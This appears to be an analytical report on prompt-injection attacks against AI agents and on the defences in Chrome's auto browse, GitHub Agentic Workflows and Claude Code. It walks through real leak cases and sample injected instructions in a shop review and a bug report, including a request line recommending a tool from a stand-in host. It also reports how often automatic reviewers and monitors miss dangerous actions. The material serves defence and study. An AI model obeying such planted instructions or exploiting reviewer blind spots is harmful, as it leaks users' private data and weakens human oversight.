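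Lockdown Mode does not stop an injected instruction from distorting answers or sending data out through an app that an administrator has enabled. Personal users can turn it off for a single chat, and it has no effect on network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported in November 2026 that Check Point had found a way around Lockdown Mode through a web-page preview. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw, which, as in EchoLeak, was in software that displayed the model's text.

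Willison (2026) welcomed Lockdown Mode's fixed rules but added that its existence implies ChatGPT's default settings do not reliably protect against a determined attacker.

### What a log would have revealed

EchoLeak had to make a web request, so a log of outgoing addresses could have recorded it. How much anyone could learn from the log would depend on who kept it and how much of each address it included:

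| Log | What it would show about EchoLeak |
|---|---|
| The company's network log, with site names only | A connection to a Microsoft service, much like ordinary office traffic |
| A log of full addresses on the employee's computer | The outside destination and the data in the address |
| Microsoft's log of outside requests by its own service | A request to an unfamiliar site, including the data |
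| A record of everything the model read and wrote | The email, the private files and the reply, but not whether the image loaded |

A company that logged only site names would have been unlikely to find the leak. Even a full address may not look suspicious if its data is encoded, and it does not show which email caused the request. To reconstruct the attack, an investigator would need to match the address with the record of what the model read. Reddy and Gujral therefore recommend logging prompts, their sources and outgoing requests.

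In 2025 the security company Radware found ShadowLeak, a flaw in OpenAI's Deep Research that let a hidden instruction in an email make the agent send out data from a user's Gmail account. The agent made the request from OpenAI's servers, so, as *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* notes, the leak might not appear in the logs of the user's browser or employer. For leaks of this kind, customers depend on the provider's logs to find out whether anyone was affected. Radware reported the flaw in June, and OpenAI had fixed it by early August, according to The Record.

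A log also records a leak only as it happens, and nobody can recall the data once the outside server has received the address. Reddy and Gujral compared defences and rated monitoring of outgoing traffic as failing to stop a zero-click leak, though they relied on published accounts and did not reproduce the attack. To prevent the leak, software has to hold the request while it checks the address. A person can intervene only if the software then waits for their answer, as OpenAI's link check does when it shows a warning.

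## Google Chrome: limits on which sites a browsing agent may read and write

A browsing agent can send data out through every page it opens and every form it fills in, as well as through its replies. Google launched one, called auto browse, on January 28, 2026, according to Bloomberg's *Google Chrome’s AI Agent Can Now Browse Web on Behalf of Users* (2026). It lets the Gemini model open websites, click and type for the user in Chrome. Seven weeks earlier, *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) had described how Google's security team planned to confine the agent.

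### Why the browser's usual separation fails

Browsers keep websites apart through the same-origin policy. An origin is a web address's scheme (such as https), host name and port number, and it corresponds roughly to one website. Code on a page from one origin cannot read a page from another, so a malicious site in one tab cannot read a bank account open in the next. The policy does not stop users from copying text between sites, so it does not stop a browsing agent from doing the same in the user's place.

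The agent sees pages as the logged-in user sees them, and what it reads stays in its context when it moves to another site. *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers* (Wang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes how data can then cross between sites even without an attacker. For example, a page may contain an iframe, which displays content from another site. If the user asks the agent to summarise the page and type the summary into a text box, the agent may give the page's owner information from the embedded site. An attacker can also plant an instruction telling the agent to type in whatever it read earlier. Both kinds of leak were frequent in the five agentic browsers the researchers tested.

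SOPGuard labels data with the site it came from and asks the user before the agent writes that data to a different site. It stopped every violation in the benchmark used to test it and added 2–6% to the running time. Trail of Bits' *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026) also recommends extending the same-origin policy to agents.

### The site sets and the gate

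Google's design keeps two sets of sites for each task. The agent can read pages on sites in the read-only set, and it can also click and type on sites in the read-writable set. Chrome doesn't show the agent content from any other site, including advertisements embedded in a permitted page. A compromised agent therefore can't read the user's webmail during a shopping task, and it can send what it has read to read-writable sites only.

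When the planning model proposes adding a site to the sets, a gate checks whether the site is relevant to the user's task, and the planner can't add it without the gate's approval. The gate never receives untrusted page text. If it did, an injection that had led the planner to try to open the user's webmail while shopping for a shirt could also lead the gate to approve webmail as relevant to the purchase.

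The gate also checks moves that the planner didn't choose, such as redirects to another site. A web address can carry private data, as in EchoLeak, so a fixed rule lets the model write only known public addresses. OpenAI's link check works similarly.

### The judging model and the user's confirmation

The site sets do not determine whether the user wants a particular action on a permitted site. Before Chrome carries out each action, a separate Gemini model called the User Alignment Critic checks whether the action serves the user's goal, then approves or vetoes it. The critic sees information about the proposed action but no unfiltered web content. After a veto, it gives the planner feedback so the planner can try something else. The planner can return control to the user if its proposals keep failing.

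Parker acknowledges that the critic has less context than the planner, but points out that its job is simpler. The critic can match "add to cart" to a request for a T-shirt, but it might not detect that the button also starts a subscription. Parker does not specify what information the critic receives. If that information includes text written by the planner, a compromised planner could use it to mislead the critic, even though no web page can send text to the critic directly.

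Chrome also checks a list of sensitive sites, such as banks and medical services, and asks the user before the agent visits one. It asks before Google Password Manager signs the agent in to a site, and the model has no direct access to the stored password. Before purchases, messages and other consequential actions, the agent "will try to pause" for permission or have the user complete the step. This protection is weaker because it partly depends on models correctly identifying which actions are consequential.

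### A shopping task

Suppose a user asks the agent to buy a plain black T-shirt in medium for less than $20. One shop's page contains an advertisement from another company and a stranger's review. The review tells any agent reading it to open the user's webmail and copy the latest message into a new review. Under the full published design, Chrome could refuse data or an action at these points:

| Step | What could be refused | What decides |
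|---|---|---|
| The agent presents its plan | The whole task | The user |
| The planner proposes a shop | The visit to the site | The gate and, for an address the model wrote, the public-address rule |
| The shop's page loads | The advertisement's content | The site sets |
| The agent reads the review | Any action based on the injected text | A classifier that scans each page for injections |
| The planner, misled by the review, proposes opening webmail | The visit to the site | The gate |
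| The planner proposes adding a shirt to the cart | The click | The critic |
| The shop asks for a login | The use of the saved password | The user |
| The agent reaches the payment page | The purchase | The user, if the agent pauses as intended |

The gate can protect the webmail without detecting the injection, because webmail is irrelevant to the request regardless of what is in the review. But suppose the review contains an instruction to post the user's delivery address, which the shop already has on file, as a public review. The shop is a permitted site, so the gate would allow the post, and the classifier, the critic or a request for confirmation would have to stop it.

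Tasks that involve many sites also weaken the sets. If the user wants to compare ten shops and the agent may write to all of them, a compromised agent can carry data from any shop to any other, which gives 10 × 9 = 90 routes. If nine of the shops are read-only, only the nine routes to the tenth shop remain. The gate could also wrongly approve an attacker's site with a plausible name, such as a T-shirt size guide, after an injection makes the planner propose it, or be too strict and block a genuine size guide.

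### What Google has shipped

Parker wrote that Google had initially built a simpler version of the gate, which tracked only the read-writable set. In the ten-shop example, that version allows all 90 routes. Google's *Ask Gemini in Chrome to complete tasks for you with auto browse* now tells users that the agent restricts itself to websites and actions relevant to the task, but does not mention a separate read-only set.

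The public code of Chromium (2025), the open-source project on which Chrome is based, gives more detail. When the agent moves to a different site, the browser makes these checks in order:

1. An employer's policy can allow or block the site, and if it does neither, Chrome's safety lists can.
2. If the site is on the sensitive list, the browser asks the user, unless the user has already approved it.
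3. The browser allows sites that the agent has already used or that Google's server has told it to use.
4. For any other site, the browser can ask the user or the server, but only if a particular setting is on.

The setting for new sites is off in Chromium's published defaults, so the browser lets the agent continue. However, Google can change these settings for users, and its server may check a site before telling the browser to open it, so the defaults don't show how strict the gate is in practice. The settings also include a "dark launch" mode. According to a comment by Chromium's developers, this mode queries the server about a new site but only logs the response. This would let Google measure how often the gate would interrupt people before enforcing its decisions.

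Since the design appeared, Google (2026) has announced another channel for Chrome called WebMCP, a proposed standard that lets websites offer agents named functions to call, so that they don't have to click through forms. Trials were due to start in Chrome 149, with support in Gemini to follow. A named function may be easier to judge than a click, but the website writes it. *WebMCP Can Be Used To Hijack AI Agents, Chrome Warns* (Montti, 2026) reports a warning in Chrome's own guidance that such tools can manipulate agents. Browser extensions are another route, which limits on websites do not cover. *BragJack Shows How Malicious Extensions Can Hijack AI Browser Agents* (Ofonagoro, 2026) describes how malicious extensions could manipulate agents in Chrome and several other products.

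### Evidence on how well it works

Google's automated systems attack the agent with malicious test sites, and Google uses the attacks' success rate to check each engineering change. Parker doesn't report those rates or how often the limits stop legitimate tasks. Google also offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for demonstrating a breach of the agent's security boundaries.

In January and February 2026, shortly after the launch, Roesner and Kohlbrenner ran independent tests of seven agentic browsers for *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* (2026). When they asked Chrome with Gemini about a page, it read iframes from other sites, although Google's full design would hide frames from sites outside the sets. It read other tabs only with the user's permission and did not read masked passwords. The researchers also asked each agent to follow a web page's instructions. ChatGPT Atlas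 complied in Agent Mode, and Chrome's agent refused.

Roesner and Kohlbrenner demonstrated a complete cross-site data theft only in Atlas. They concluded that Chrome met the preconditions for the same attack, so its safety depended on how well it resisted prompt injection. Because they had no working injection for Chrome, they could not test whether the critic or the gate would have stopped one. They also found it unclear how Google determines relevance, or how well that decision withstands malicious input. Google acknowledged their report. In an April update, Roesner and Kohlbrenner advised caution with agentic browsers in general and called Chrome's agent one of the more powerful and riskier ones.

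Tests of a different detector suggest that page scanning is a weak defence against persistent attackers. *BrowseSafe++* (2026) tested a detector that screened pages before an agent using Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite read them. The detector blocked 94.5% of the original injections, but an automated attacker that could revise its text and try up to 64 times still succeeded in 84.2% of 1,024 tasks, compared with 93.6% without the detector. Chrome's classifier may perform better, but Google has published no comparable figure.

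### SPIDES: labels within a page

*SPIDES* (Zverev, Kim and colleagues, 2026) brings the labels used in Fides to web pages. The owner of a website labels each part of a page to show whether the content is trusted and which sites may receive it. For example, a shop would mark its prices as trusted, customer reviews as untrusted, and the user's saved card number as readable only by the user and the shop. As in Fides, the agent sees the prices, but variables hide the reviews and the card number until the agent opens them.

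The user lists the sites whose owners they trust, and SPIDES assumes that the user has accounts only on those sites. A click or form submission on a listed site could use the user's account, so SPIDES allows it without asking the user only if no untrusted text has influenced it. SPIDES allows typing without submitting, and any action on an unlisted site, if no untrusted text has influenced the action or if the site is permitted to receive the data. Clicks and submissions that don't meet these conditions need the user's approval. SPIDES always blocks tools that run arbitrary code.

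Two test cases show why the boundary between sites is a poor guide to harm. In one, a malicious message on a social network told the agent to copy the user's private recovery email address into their public profile. SOPGuard allowed this in all 25 runs because the data never left the site. SPIDES let the agent type the address but not click "Save changes", because untrusted text had influenced the click. In the other, the user wanted to check a discount by looking up the product on a second site. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs, and SPIDES in four.

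Zverev and colleagues built a benchmark of 28 linked websites with 56 ordinary tasks and 56 attacks, and ran it with five recent models. For most attacks, they assumed the worst case. Whenever the attacker's text reached the main model, they replaced the model's next actions with ones the attacker would choose, so the results measure the enforcement and not the model's resistance. Besides SOPGuard, they tested UCM, which hides untrusted text but lets restricted answers about it influence the agent. The table gives the lowest and highest averages among the five models:

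| Defence | Successful attacks | Ordinary tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| None | 57.5–95.7% | 58.2–91.1% |
| SOPGuard | 53.2–73.2% | 58.2–93.2% |
| UCM | 4.6–6.8% | 42.9–67.5% |
| SPIDES | 0% | 67.1–86.1% |

SPIDES reduced the task completion rate by 5 to 11 percentage points for three models. With Claude Opus 5.5, it completed more tasks than the unprotected agent, partly because hiding login details avoided some refusals by the provider's safety filter. SPIDES required 1.84 user approvals per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard. The experiment assumed that users always answer approval requests correctly. The estimated cost per task was $0.37–1.42, roughly twice that of the unprotected agent.

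The study did not include Chrome. SOPGuard also draws its boundaries between sites, but it has no critic, relevance gate or page classifier, so its attack rates are not estimates of Chrome's. Google's approach is more practical in that it works on websites as they are. SPIDES depends on website owners to label their pages and keep the labels correct, which the researchers could guarantee only because they wrote all 28 sites. Its labels also identify sites rather than people, so they can't always distinguish the right recipient from the wrong one within the same site.

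### What the user can see and stop

Chrome shows the user the agent's plan, and the agent begins only after the user clicks "Start Task." A log lists each step as it happens, and an icon marks the tab in use. The user can take over the task and hand it back, or end it by clicking "Stop" or closing the tab. These are browser controls, so unlike Yue's attempts to stop OpenClaw, they don't rely on the model obeying a message.

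Google says the agent aims to ask before it submits forms, sends communications or changes the user's data. The agent may hand over to the user to make final payments, create accounts or accept terms of service. Google also warns that the agent might complete a purchase without permission, and calls monitoring the most important protection. Monitoring is demanding for heavy users. Subscribers to Google's most expensive plan can request up to 200 tasks a day and run several at once, and watching 200 tasks for one minute each would take three hours and 20 minutes. The browser history marks the sites the agent visited, so the user can find unexpected visits afterwards, but it does not show what the agent typed there.

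## GitHub Agentic Workflows: the agent proposes, a separate job writes

In GitHub Agentic Workflows, an AI agent can read a software project but cannot change it. The agent files structured requests, such as "open an issue with this title and text". After it finishes, a separate job with write permission checks the requests and carries them out. This delay is acceptable because most changes to a software project can wait a few minutes. Chrome, by contrast, has to check a browsing agent's actions one at a time, because each click determines what the agent sees next.

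GitHub hosts software projects in repositories, where people report bugs as issues and propose code changes as pull requests. It launched Agentic Workflows in 2026 for work such as sorting issues, investigating failed tests and updating documentation. The project's owner writes the agent's instructions in ordinary language and adds settings. A compiler turns these into a series of jobs for GitHub Actions, the company's automation service.

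Programs in GitHub Actions normally share one set of permissions and secrets. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) warns that an agent misled by an injection could use this access to find passwords and publish them. GitHub therefore designed Agentic Workflows on the assumption that the agent will try to read and change things it shouldn't and will misuse the channels it is allowed to use.

### Three jobs with different permissions

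GitHub's *Security Architecture* divides the main part of a run among three jobs:

| Job | What it works on | What it may change | What it produces |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent | The repository, the issue that started the run and permitted websites | Nothing in the project | A file of requests and any proposed code changes |
| Threat detection | The agent's requests and code changes, and the owner's instructions | Nothing in the project | A verdict |
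| Safe outputs | The requests, if the verdict allows them | Only what the request types need, such as issues for a comment | Changes to the project |

The agent works in a sandbox, and its web traffic must pass through a proxy with an allowlist. GitHub keeps passwords and access keys outside the sandbox. A separate program adds the language model's key to the agent's calls, so the agent can use the model without seeing the key. Malicious code in the sandbox could still use the model through that program. GitHub also says the design is not meant to stop side-channel attacks.

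A separate filter restricts what the agent reads. In public repositories, the agent's GitHub tools return only material from the project's owners, members and collaborators by default. The filter selects material by author, not by wording. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* describes it as the counterpart of safe outputs. The default doesn't suit an agent that sorts strangers' bug reports, so the agent's owner has to relax the filter or put the text of each report directly into the prompt.

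### Request types, caps and checks

GitHub's *Safe Outputs* lists more than 50 types of request, and the owner chooses which of them a workflow may use. Most types have a default cap per run, such as one new issue or one comment. The agent may make five requests to add labels, each with up to ten labels, for a total of 50. Alerts about security flaws in code have no default cap.

An owner can also restrict what a request contains, for instance by listing the permitted labels. Labels matter because some projects use them to start other automated workflows, which may have more permissions than the agent. Owners can also block labels by name pattern, which overrides the permitted list.

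GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* (2026) sets the order in which software must check each request:

1. The request has the required fields, in the right format.
2. The number of requests is within the cap.
3. Software cleans the text.
4. Software removes links to sites that are not on the allowlist.
5. The request concerns a permitted repository.
6. Any references to other issues or requests are valid.
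7. Only then does the job make the change.

If the agent exceeds a cap, the software rejects the whole batch instead of carrying out the first few requests. An attacker therefore can't get a harmful comment posted by having the agent file it first, but can block a genuine comment by making the agent file too many.

Cleaning replaces the address of an unlisted site with "(redacted)", so a comment can't load an image from an attacker's server, as EchoLeak's replies did. It also removes hidden comments and disables most mentions of people outside the project, who would otherwise receive notifications. Another step searches the agent's files for exact matches to the project's known passwords and keys. GitHub acknowledges that this search may miss disguised credentials.

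The threat scan runs before the writing job. According to GitHub's *Threat Detection*, a model reads the requests and answers yes or no to whether they show signs of prompt injection, a leaked secret or a malicious code change. By default, a single "yes" blocks all the requests, and they are also blocked if the scan itself fails. The scan uses the same AI engine as the agent unless configured otherwise, so text that misled the agent may also mislead the scanner. Owners can add conventional security scanners or turn the scan off.

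### A bug report with an injected instruction

GitHub's documentation includes a workflow that reads each new issue and may post up to two comments. A slightly different version could sort bug reports with these settings:

```
on:
  issues:
    types: [opened]
permissions:
  contents: read
  issues: read
safe-outputs:
  add-labels:
    allowed: [bug, question, duplicate]
  add-comment:
    max: 1
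```

Suppose a stranger reports that the program crashes when it opens large files. In the report, the stranger also tells any agent reading it to close issue 41, mark the new report as approved for release, and recommend a "repair tool" from an outside website. In the worst case, the agent follows these instructions and the scan misses them.

The agent has no tool for closing issues, because the owner did not list that type of request. It can file only these:

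```
{"type": "add_labels", "labels": ["bug"]}
{"type": "add_labels", "labels": ["release-approved"]}
{"type": "add_comment", "body": "Install the repair tool from https://tool.example"}
```

The writing job adds the label "bug" and rejects "release-approved". It posts the comment but replaces the address with "(redacted)". If the agent had also filed a comment for issue 41, the job would have rejected both comments for exceeding the cap. A single comment couldn't have gone to issue 41 either, because by default comments go only to the issue that started the run.

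The project now has a comment recommending a tool that doesn't exist or is malicious. The fixed checks can't detect that the recommendation is false, and a reader might search for the tool by name. GitHub accepts this risk in its specification, noting that an agent may write plausible but inappropriate text within its limits.

The caps also apply to each run separately, so an attacker who opens 100 issues can cause 100 comments. GitHub's *Rate Limiting Controls* describes a setting that limits how often one user can start runs, for example to five an hour, but an attacker with ten accounts could still start 50 an hour. A daily spending cap, by default about $50 for each workflow, limits the total. In sample figures on GitHub's home page for the product, six issue-sorting runs cost $2.57, or about 43 cents each. At that rate, the cap would allow roughly 117 runs a day. Once a workflow reaches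 the cap, GitHub skips the agent, so genuine reports go unsorted too.

### Private data in a permitted comment

GitHub says on its home page that the design cuts off all three parts of the lethal trifecta, but in its diagram it counts only secrets and credentials as private data, which leaves out private source code and documents. A public comment is also an outgoing channel, and so is a new issue, whose text can have up to 65,000 characters, more than 30 times the length of the 2,000-character web address discussed earlier.

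In July 2026, Noma Security showed that attackers could exploit this gap, and named the finding GitLost. InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) describes the setup. The workflow started when someone assigned an issue. It read the issue's title and text and could post a comment in reply. It also had permission to read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones.

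The researchers opened a public issue that looked like a request from the company's sales leadership. The agent fetched a file from a private repository and posted its contents in a public comment. GitHub had protections against this, but the researchers tried different wordings until one worked, according to SecurityWeek's *Critical Vulnerability Exposes GitHub Agentic Workflows to Prompt Injection*. Separating reading from writing did not prevent the leak, because the leak used a type of request the owner had allowed.

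By default, the agent's GitHub tools can read only the current repository and public ones. GitHub's documentation says that access to other private repositories requires an additional credential, so someone must have supplied one. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) therefore treats the workflow as misconfigured. Software can block the leak without recognising the injection. The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reports Noma's view that the flaw cannot be fixed in code, but this is true only of the model's tendency to follow injected instructions.

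The October 2026 version of GitHub's specification describes such a block, which by default restricts the flow of data from private repositories to public places. Like the permitted-flow rule in Fides, it depends on who can see the destination, not on the text's content. Owners can turn it off, although the compiler's strict mode rejects workflows that turn it off. Owners can also limit the agent's reading to the current repository. In a public project, the agent then can't read any private repositories, which it rarely needs for sorting bug reports.

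### Flaws in similar systems

In May 2025, before GitLost, the security company Invariant Labs found a similar attack, in which a malicious public issue could make a user's agent leak private repositories through GitHub's standard connection for AI tools. BeyondMachines' *GitHub AI integration allows attackers to access private repository data* (2025) advised users to give an agent access only to the repositories it needs.

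In December 2025, Aikido Security reported flaws in automated workflows that used AI agents on GitHub and GitLab. In a test of the workflow for Gemini CLI, Google's coding agent, an injected instruction could make the agent publish an access key by editing an issue. Google fixed the workflow within four days, according to HEAL Security. The attack was possible because the agent had access to the key and could edit the issue directly. Agentic Workflows is designed to prevent both by keeping keys out of the sandbox and leaving edits to the writing job.

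Researchers had also reported a flaw in Anthropic's Claude Code in October 2025, and Anthropic released a fix that November, according to BestHub's *Prompt Injection Threat*. Microsoft described another flaw in Claude Code Action, which runs Anthropic's agent in GitHub workflows. An attacker who influenced the agent might have directed its file-reading tool to sensitive files on the machine running the workflow. Read-only permission does not prevent this exposure, so GitHub's design also hides selected files from the agent.

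### Reviewing changes before they happen

Every change starts as a request, so a monitor can examine it before it takes effect. GitHub's specification gives this as a reason for using structured requests instead of letting the agent run commands.

Owners can use the interval to review or stop the proposed changes. In staged mode, the workflow only shows what it would have done. For a code change, the preview lists the branch and summarises the edits, according to GitHub's *Staged Mode*. If a workflow makes real changes, the owner can require a person's approval or set a waiting period before the writing job starts. If someone cancels the run before that job starts, none of the requested changes takes place. Yue had no such interval because OpenClaw deleted her mail as it worked.

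GitHub doesn't require human approval by default because, according to its specification, approving everything by hand would defeat the purpose of automation. Pull requests are a compromise that lets the agent propose a code change without adding it to the project. GitHub's *Safe Outputs (Pull Requests)* sets a default limit of 100 files per pull request, which is still a lot to review. Owners can also let a workflow merge pull requests automatically, so a change may take effect before anyone sees it.

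The saved requests also let people correct the scanner's mistakes. If it blocks a harmless comment, a project administrator or maintainer can replay the requests without running the agent again. But replaying can also apply requests that the scanner blocked for good reason, so the person doing it needs to read them first. If a change fails during the writing job, GitHub does not undo the changes already completed.

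For later investigations, GitHub logs network connections, model calls and tool calls at separate points outside the agent. Together with the saved requests, these logs could reveal a leak by showing that an agent read a private file shortly before it asked to post a public comment.

### Tasks that cannot wait

Staging works when the agent doesn't need to see the result of a change before deciding what to do next. The agent can still propose an issue and a comment that mentions it, using a temporary name that the writing job replaces with the real issue number. It can also make one request depend on another, so that the comment appears only if the issue was created.

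These methods don't help if the next step depends on an outside service's reply. An agent that books a meeting room must know whether the booking succeeded before it tells the participants where to go. An agent that buys a T-shirt has to put it in the cart before the shop shows the delivery charge. A customer-service agent may need to ask a question and read the answer. In each case the agent has to send something out during the run, and delaying it would stop the work.

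Some of these tasks can be split into steps. GitHub's *Custom Safe Outputs* describes an agent that searches the note-taking service Notion with read-only tools, then leaves a request for a later job to add a comment. In the same way, an agent could check which rooms are free and request a booking, and a second run could read the result and notify the participants. The second run takes extra time and starts with a new context, and somebody else may book the room before the agent's request is processed.

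Searches also have to happen during the run, and staging doesn't check search terms for private data. So for services outside GitHub, protection depends on which sites and tools the owner has allowed.

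## Claude Code: sandboxes, permission prompts and automatic reviewers

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, edits a program, runs its tests, reads the errors and edits again. It needs the result of almost every action to choose the next one, so it cannot use the approach of GitHub Agentic Workflows, where a separate job holds the agent's changes until the end of the run. Claude Code usually works on the developer's own computer and can use the shell, the program that carries out typed commands. A single command can delete a folder, install software or send a file to a website.

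Anthropic has added three controls over these actions. Permission prompts let the user approve or reject an action before it runs. A sandbox limits the files and websites that commands can reach. An automatic reviewer, a separate model, approves or blocks actions in the user's place.

### Permission prompts and approval fatigue

Under the original settings, Claude Code could read files freely but had to ask before it changed a file or ran a command. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* mentions a few exceptions for harmless commands, such as one that displays a file. Users could also set rules that let certain commands run without a prompt.

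According to Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products*, approval fatigue appeared within weeks: the more prompts users saw, the less attention they paid to each. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of prompts, and its later *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports 97%. A high acceptance rate does not prove carelessness, because most commands are safe. Users rejected 39% of the plans Claude Code presented for approval, compared with 3% of the prompts for single actions, so they evidently do object when they have something larger to judge.

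Anthropic also tested attention directly, in a coding study with 1,053 paid testers who were not told which behaviour it was measuring. Partway through each session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one, and 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The overall rate may be too pessimistic, because the testers were not working on their own projects and had less to lose than a developer at work. The decline during sessions is stronger evidence of fatigue, because the stakes stayed the same.

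Many users avoid some or all of the prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a standing rule that let certain shell commands run without a prompt. Many of these rules allowed everything run through a programming language such as Python, which permits practically any action. A quarter of interactive sessions started with all prompts turned off.

Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) found a similar trend as users gained experience. Users with fewer than 50 sessions let the agent run without manual approval in about 20% of sessions, while those with 750 did so in more than 40%. Experienced users also interrupted the agent more often, in about 9% of turns compared with 5% for new users. Anthropic interprets this as a change from approving each step to watching and intervening. But the most common reason for interrupting, at 32%,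 was to supply missing technical context or corrections, and another 17% of interruptions came when the agent was slow, stuck or doing too much. The study therefore shows that experienced users stay involved, but it doesn't show that they would catch a dangerous command in time.

### The sandbox

In October 2025, Anthropic introduced a sandbox for shell commands. By default, commands can read files across the computer but change only those in the project folder. They can reach the internet only through a proxy outside the sandbox, which checks each destination against an allowlist and asks the user about new sites. The operating system enforces these limits, so they also apply to any program a command starts.

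The sandbox's file and network limits are each weak without the other. With file limits alone, an agent misled by a prompt injection could read a private key and send it to an outsider. If only network access were limited, the agent could tamper with the rest of the system and escape the sandbox, which would remove the network limits too.

The sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84% in Anthropic's internal use, because commands that stay within its limits need no approval. Anthropic did not report how many harmful actions the sandbox stopped or how much legitimate work it blocked.

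Like GitHub Agentic Workflows, the version of Claude Code that runs on Anthropic's servers keeps real credentials outside the sandbox. The agent gets a substitute credential that works only with a proxy. The proxy checks that the agent is sending its changes to the permitted branch (a separate line of work within the project) before adding the real credential.

As with EchoLeak, a permitted site can provide a way around the network limit, so Anthropic now treats each allowlist entry as permission to use every function the site offers. The software that enforces the limit can also fail. Anthropic reports that long-established isolation software has held up well in its products, but a filter it wrote itself has failed. Smalley (2026) reported in *Sandbox vulnerability gives rogue AI agents a path to escape* that the security company AIR disclosed a flaw in October 2026 in the network filter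 of Vercel Sandbox, a widely used product. The flaw could let data leave for unapproved destinations.

### A leak from two harmless steps

A sandbox that works perfectly can still allow a leak. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to set up a new project by copying a settings file from an old one, and later to publish the new project on GitHub. The settings file contains a secret key for an online service. Copying the file is harmless because it stays on the user's computer, and the user did ask to publish the project, but together the two steps make the key public. The researchers saw Claude 4.5 Haiku do this without any attacker involved.

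File and network limits do not prevent this leak. The copy changes only the project folder, and GitHub has to be on the allowlist for the user to publish there.

Adam and colleagues propose a separate policy for each tool call. Before a tool is used, an automatic analysis of its code lists the effects it can have, such as writing files or contacting websites. The tool's developer puts a small sandbox around each operation with such an effect, and each call's policy sets the limits for these sandboxes. Once the key is in the project, the policy for publishing can hide the settings file while still allowing the rest of the project to be published.

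A prototype was tested on three scenarios, each with an acceptable and an unacceptable version. Anthropic's sandbox, with one fixed policy for the whole session, gave the right result in three of the six cases. It let the key leak, and in another scenario it blocked a change the user had requested to a startup file. The prototype was right in all six. But the test was small, used recorded sessions, and assumed that the prototype had already been given the correct policy for every call, which still requires someone or something to recognise that the settings file contains a secret.

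### The automatic reviewer

In March 2026, Anthropic described auto mode, in which a model, rather than the user, reviews actions. By November 12, it was the starting mode for interactive sessions on every plan, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), although some configurations still started with manual prompts.

Claude Code sorts actions as follows:

1. Actions that only read, and those that the user's narrow rules allow, run without review. Auto mode suspends rules broad enough to permit almost any command.
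2. Edits within the project folder also run without review, because the user can inspect them later in the project's version history.
3. Shell commands, web requests, changes outside the folder and other remaining actions go to the reviewer.

The reviewer first makes a quick yes-or-no decision, with instructions to block when in doubt. If it decides to block, it reviews the same material again, this time reasoning before it gives a final answer. Its default rules cover more than 20 kinds of action, including destroying data, sending internal data out, disabling logs and bypassing safety checks. It must also decide whether the user authorised the specific action. A request to "clean up old branches", for example, does not authorise the agent to delete them from the team's shared server.

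In the design Anthropic published, the reviewer reads only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Claude Code removes the agent's explanations so the agent cannot talk the reviewer into a bad decision. It removes tool results because injected instructions arrive through them, and the reviewer rarely needs them. If a file tells the agent to send passwords to an outside address, the reviewer can block the tool call without seeing the file, because the user never asked for it. The gate in Chrome excludes page text for the same reason.

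The reviewer does not see the agent's explanations or tool results, so if the agent cancels a job whose number the user never mentioned, the reviewer cannot determine whether the number came from a search result or the agent made it up. However, when Anthropic included the explanations and results, the reviewer became worse at catching actions that exceeded the user's request. A version given only tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked things that users had plainly asked for.

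Anthropic has since given the reviewer more facts about the agent's surroundings, such as whether a repository is public and whether a command would discard unsaved work. It has also added a category of actions that the reviewer should never approve, including sending secrets to outsiders. Users can run these only by leaving auto mode or entering the command themselves. A different model scans tool results for injections and warns the agent about suspicious text.

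When the reviewer blocks an action, the agent receives the reason and an instruction to find a safer way. After three blocks in a row, or 20 in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user for permission, or ends the run if it is unattended.

### A session of 200 actions

Anthropic measured wrongly blocked actions on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees. It measured missed actions on 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond the user's request, and on 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out. Suppose the reviewer examines all 200 actions in a session, of which 199 are harmless and one is dangerous. The table applies these rates to the session, along with those from the study of testers:

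| Who or what checks the actions | Harmless actions wrongly blocked | Chance that the dangerous action runs | Dangerous actions used to measure this |
|---|---|---|---|
| A person answering prompts | Not reported | 86% | Commands shown to the testers |
| Auto mode | Not reported | 11% | Commands shown to the testers |
| Auto mode, quick decision only | 16.9 | 6.6% | 52 real cases |
| Auto mode, complete review | 0.8 | 17% | 52 real cases |
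| Auto mode, complete review | 0.8 | 5.7% | 1,000 artificial data leaks |

The second look reduces the wrong blocks from about 17 to fewer than one, but lets more dangerous actions through. With the complete review, there is about a 55% chance of at least one wrong block in the session, after which the agent typically has to try again. The 17% miss rate matters more, because over four such sessions there is a 53% chance that at least one dangerous action runs. That rate is uncertain because it comes from only 52 cases, and the true figure could plausibly be from about 9% to 30%.

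In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented. The user might have approved a similar action earlier, or made a general request that did not cover the action in question. Anthropic tried to fix this by rewording the reviewer's instructions, but found no change that was worth its side effects.

Dangerous actions are usually much rarer than one in 200. If they were one in 2,000, the reviewer would stop about eight of the ten dangerous actions in every 20,000 and wrongly block about 80 harmless ones. Roughly nine in ten blocks would be false alarms. A user who had to rule on each block would soon be fatigued again, so it makes sense to send blocks back to the agent first.

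In the study of testers, auto mode's reviewer blocked 937 of the 1,053 commands. The testers caught only six of the 116 it missed, though a careful person could have caught many more. Using both the reviewer and the testers would have raised the share caught from 89.0% to 89.6%.

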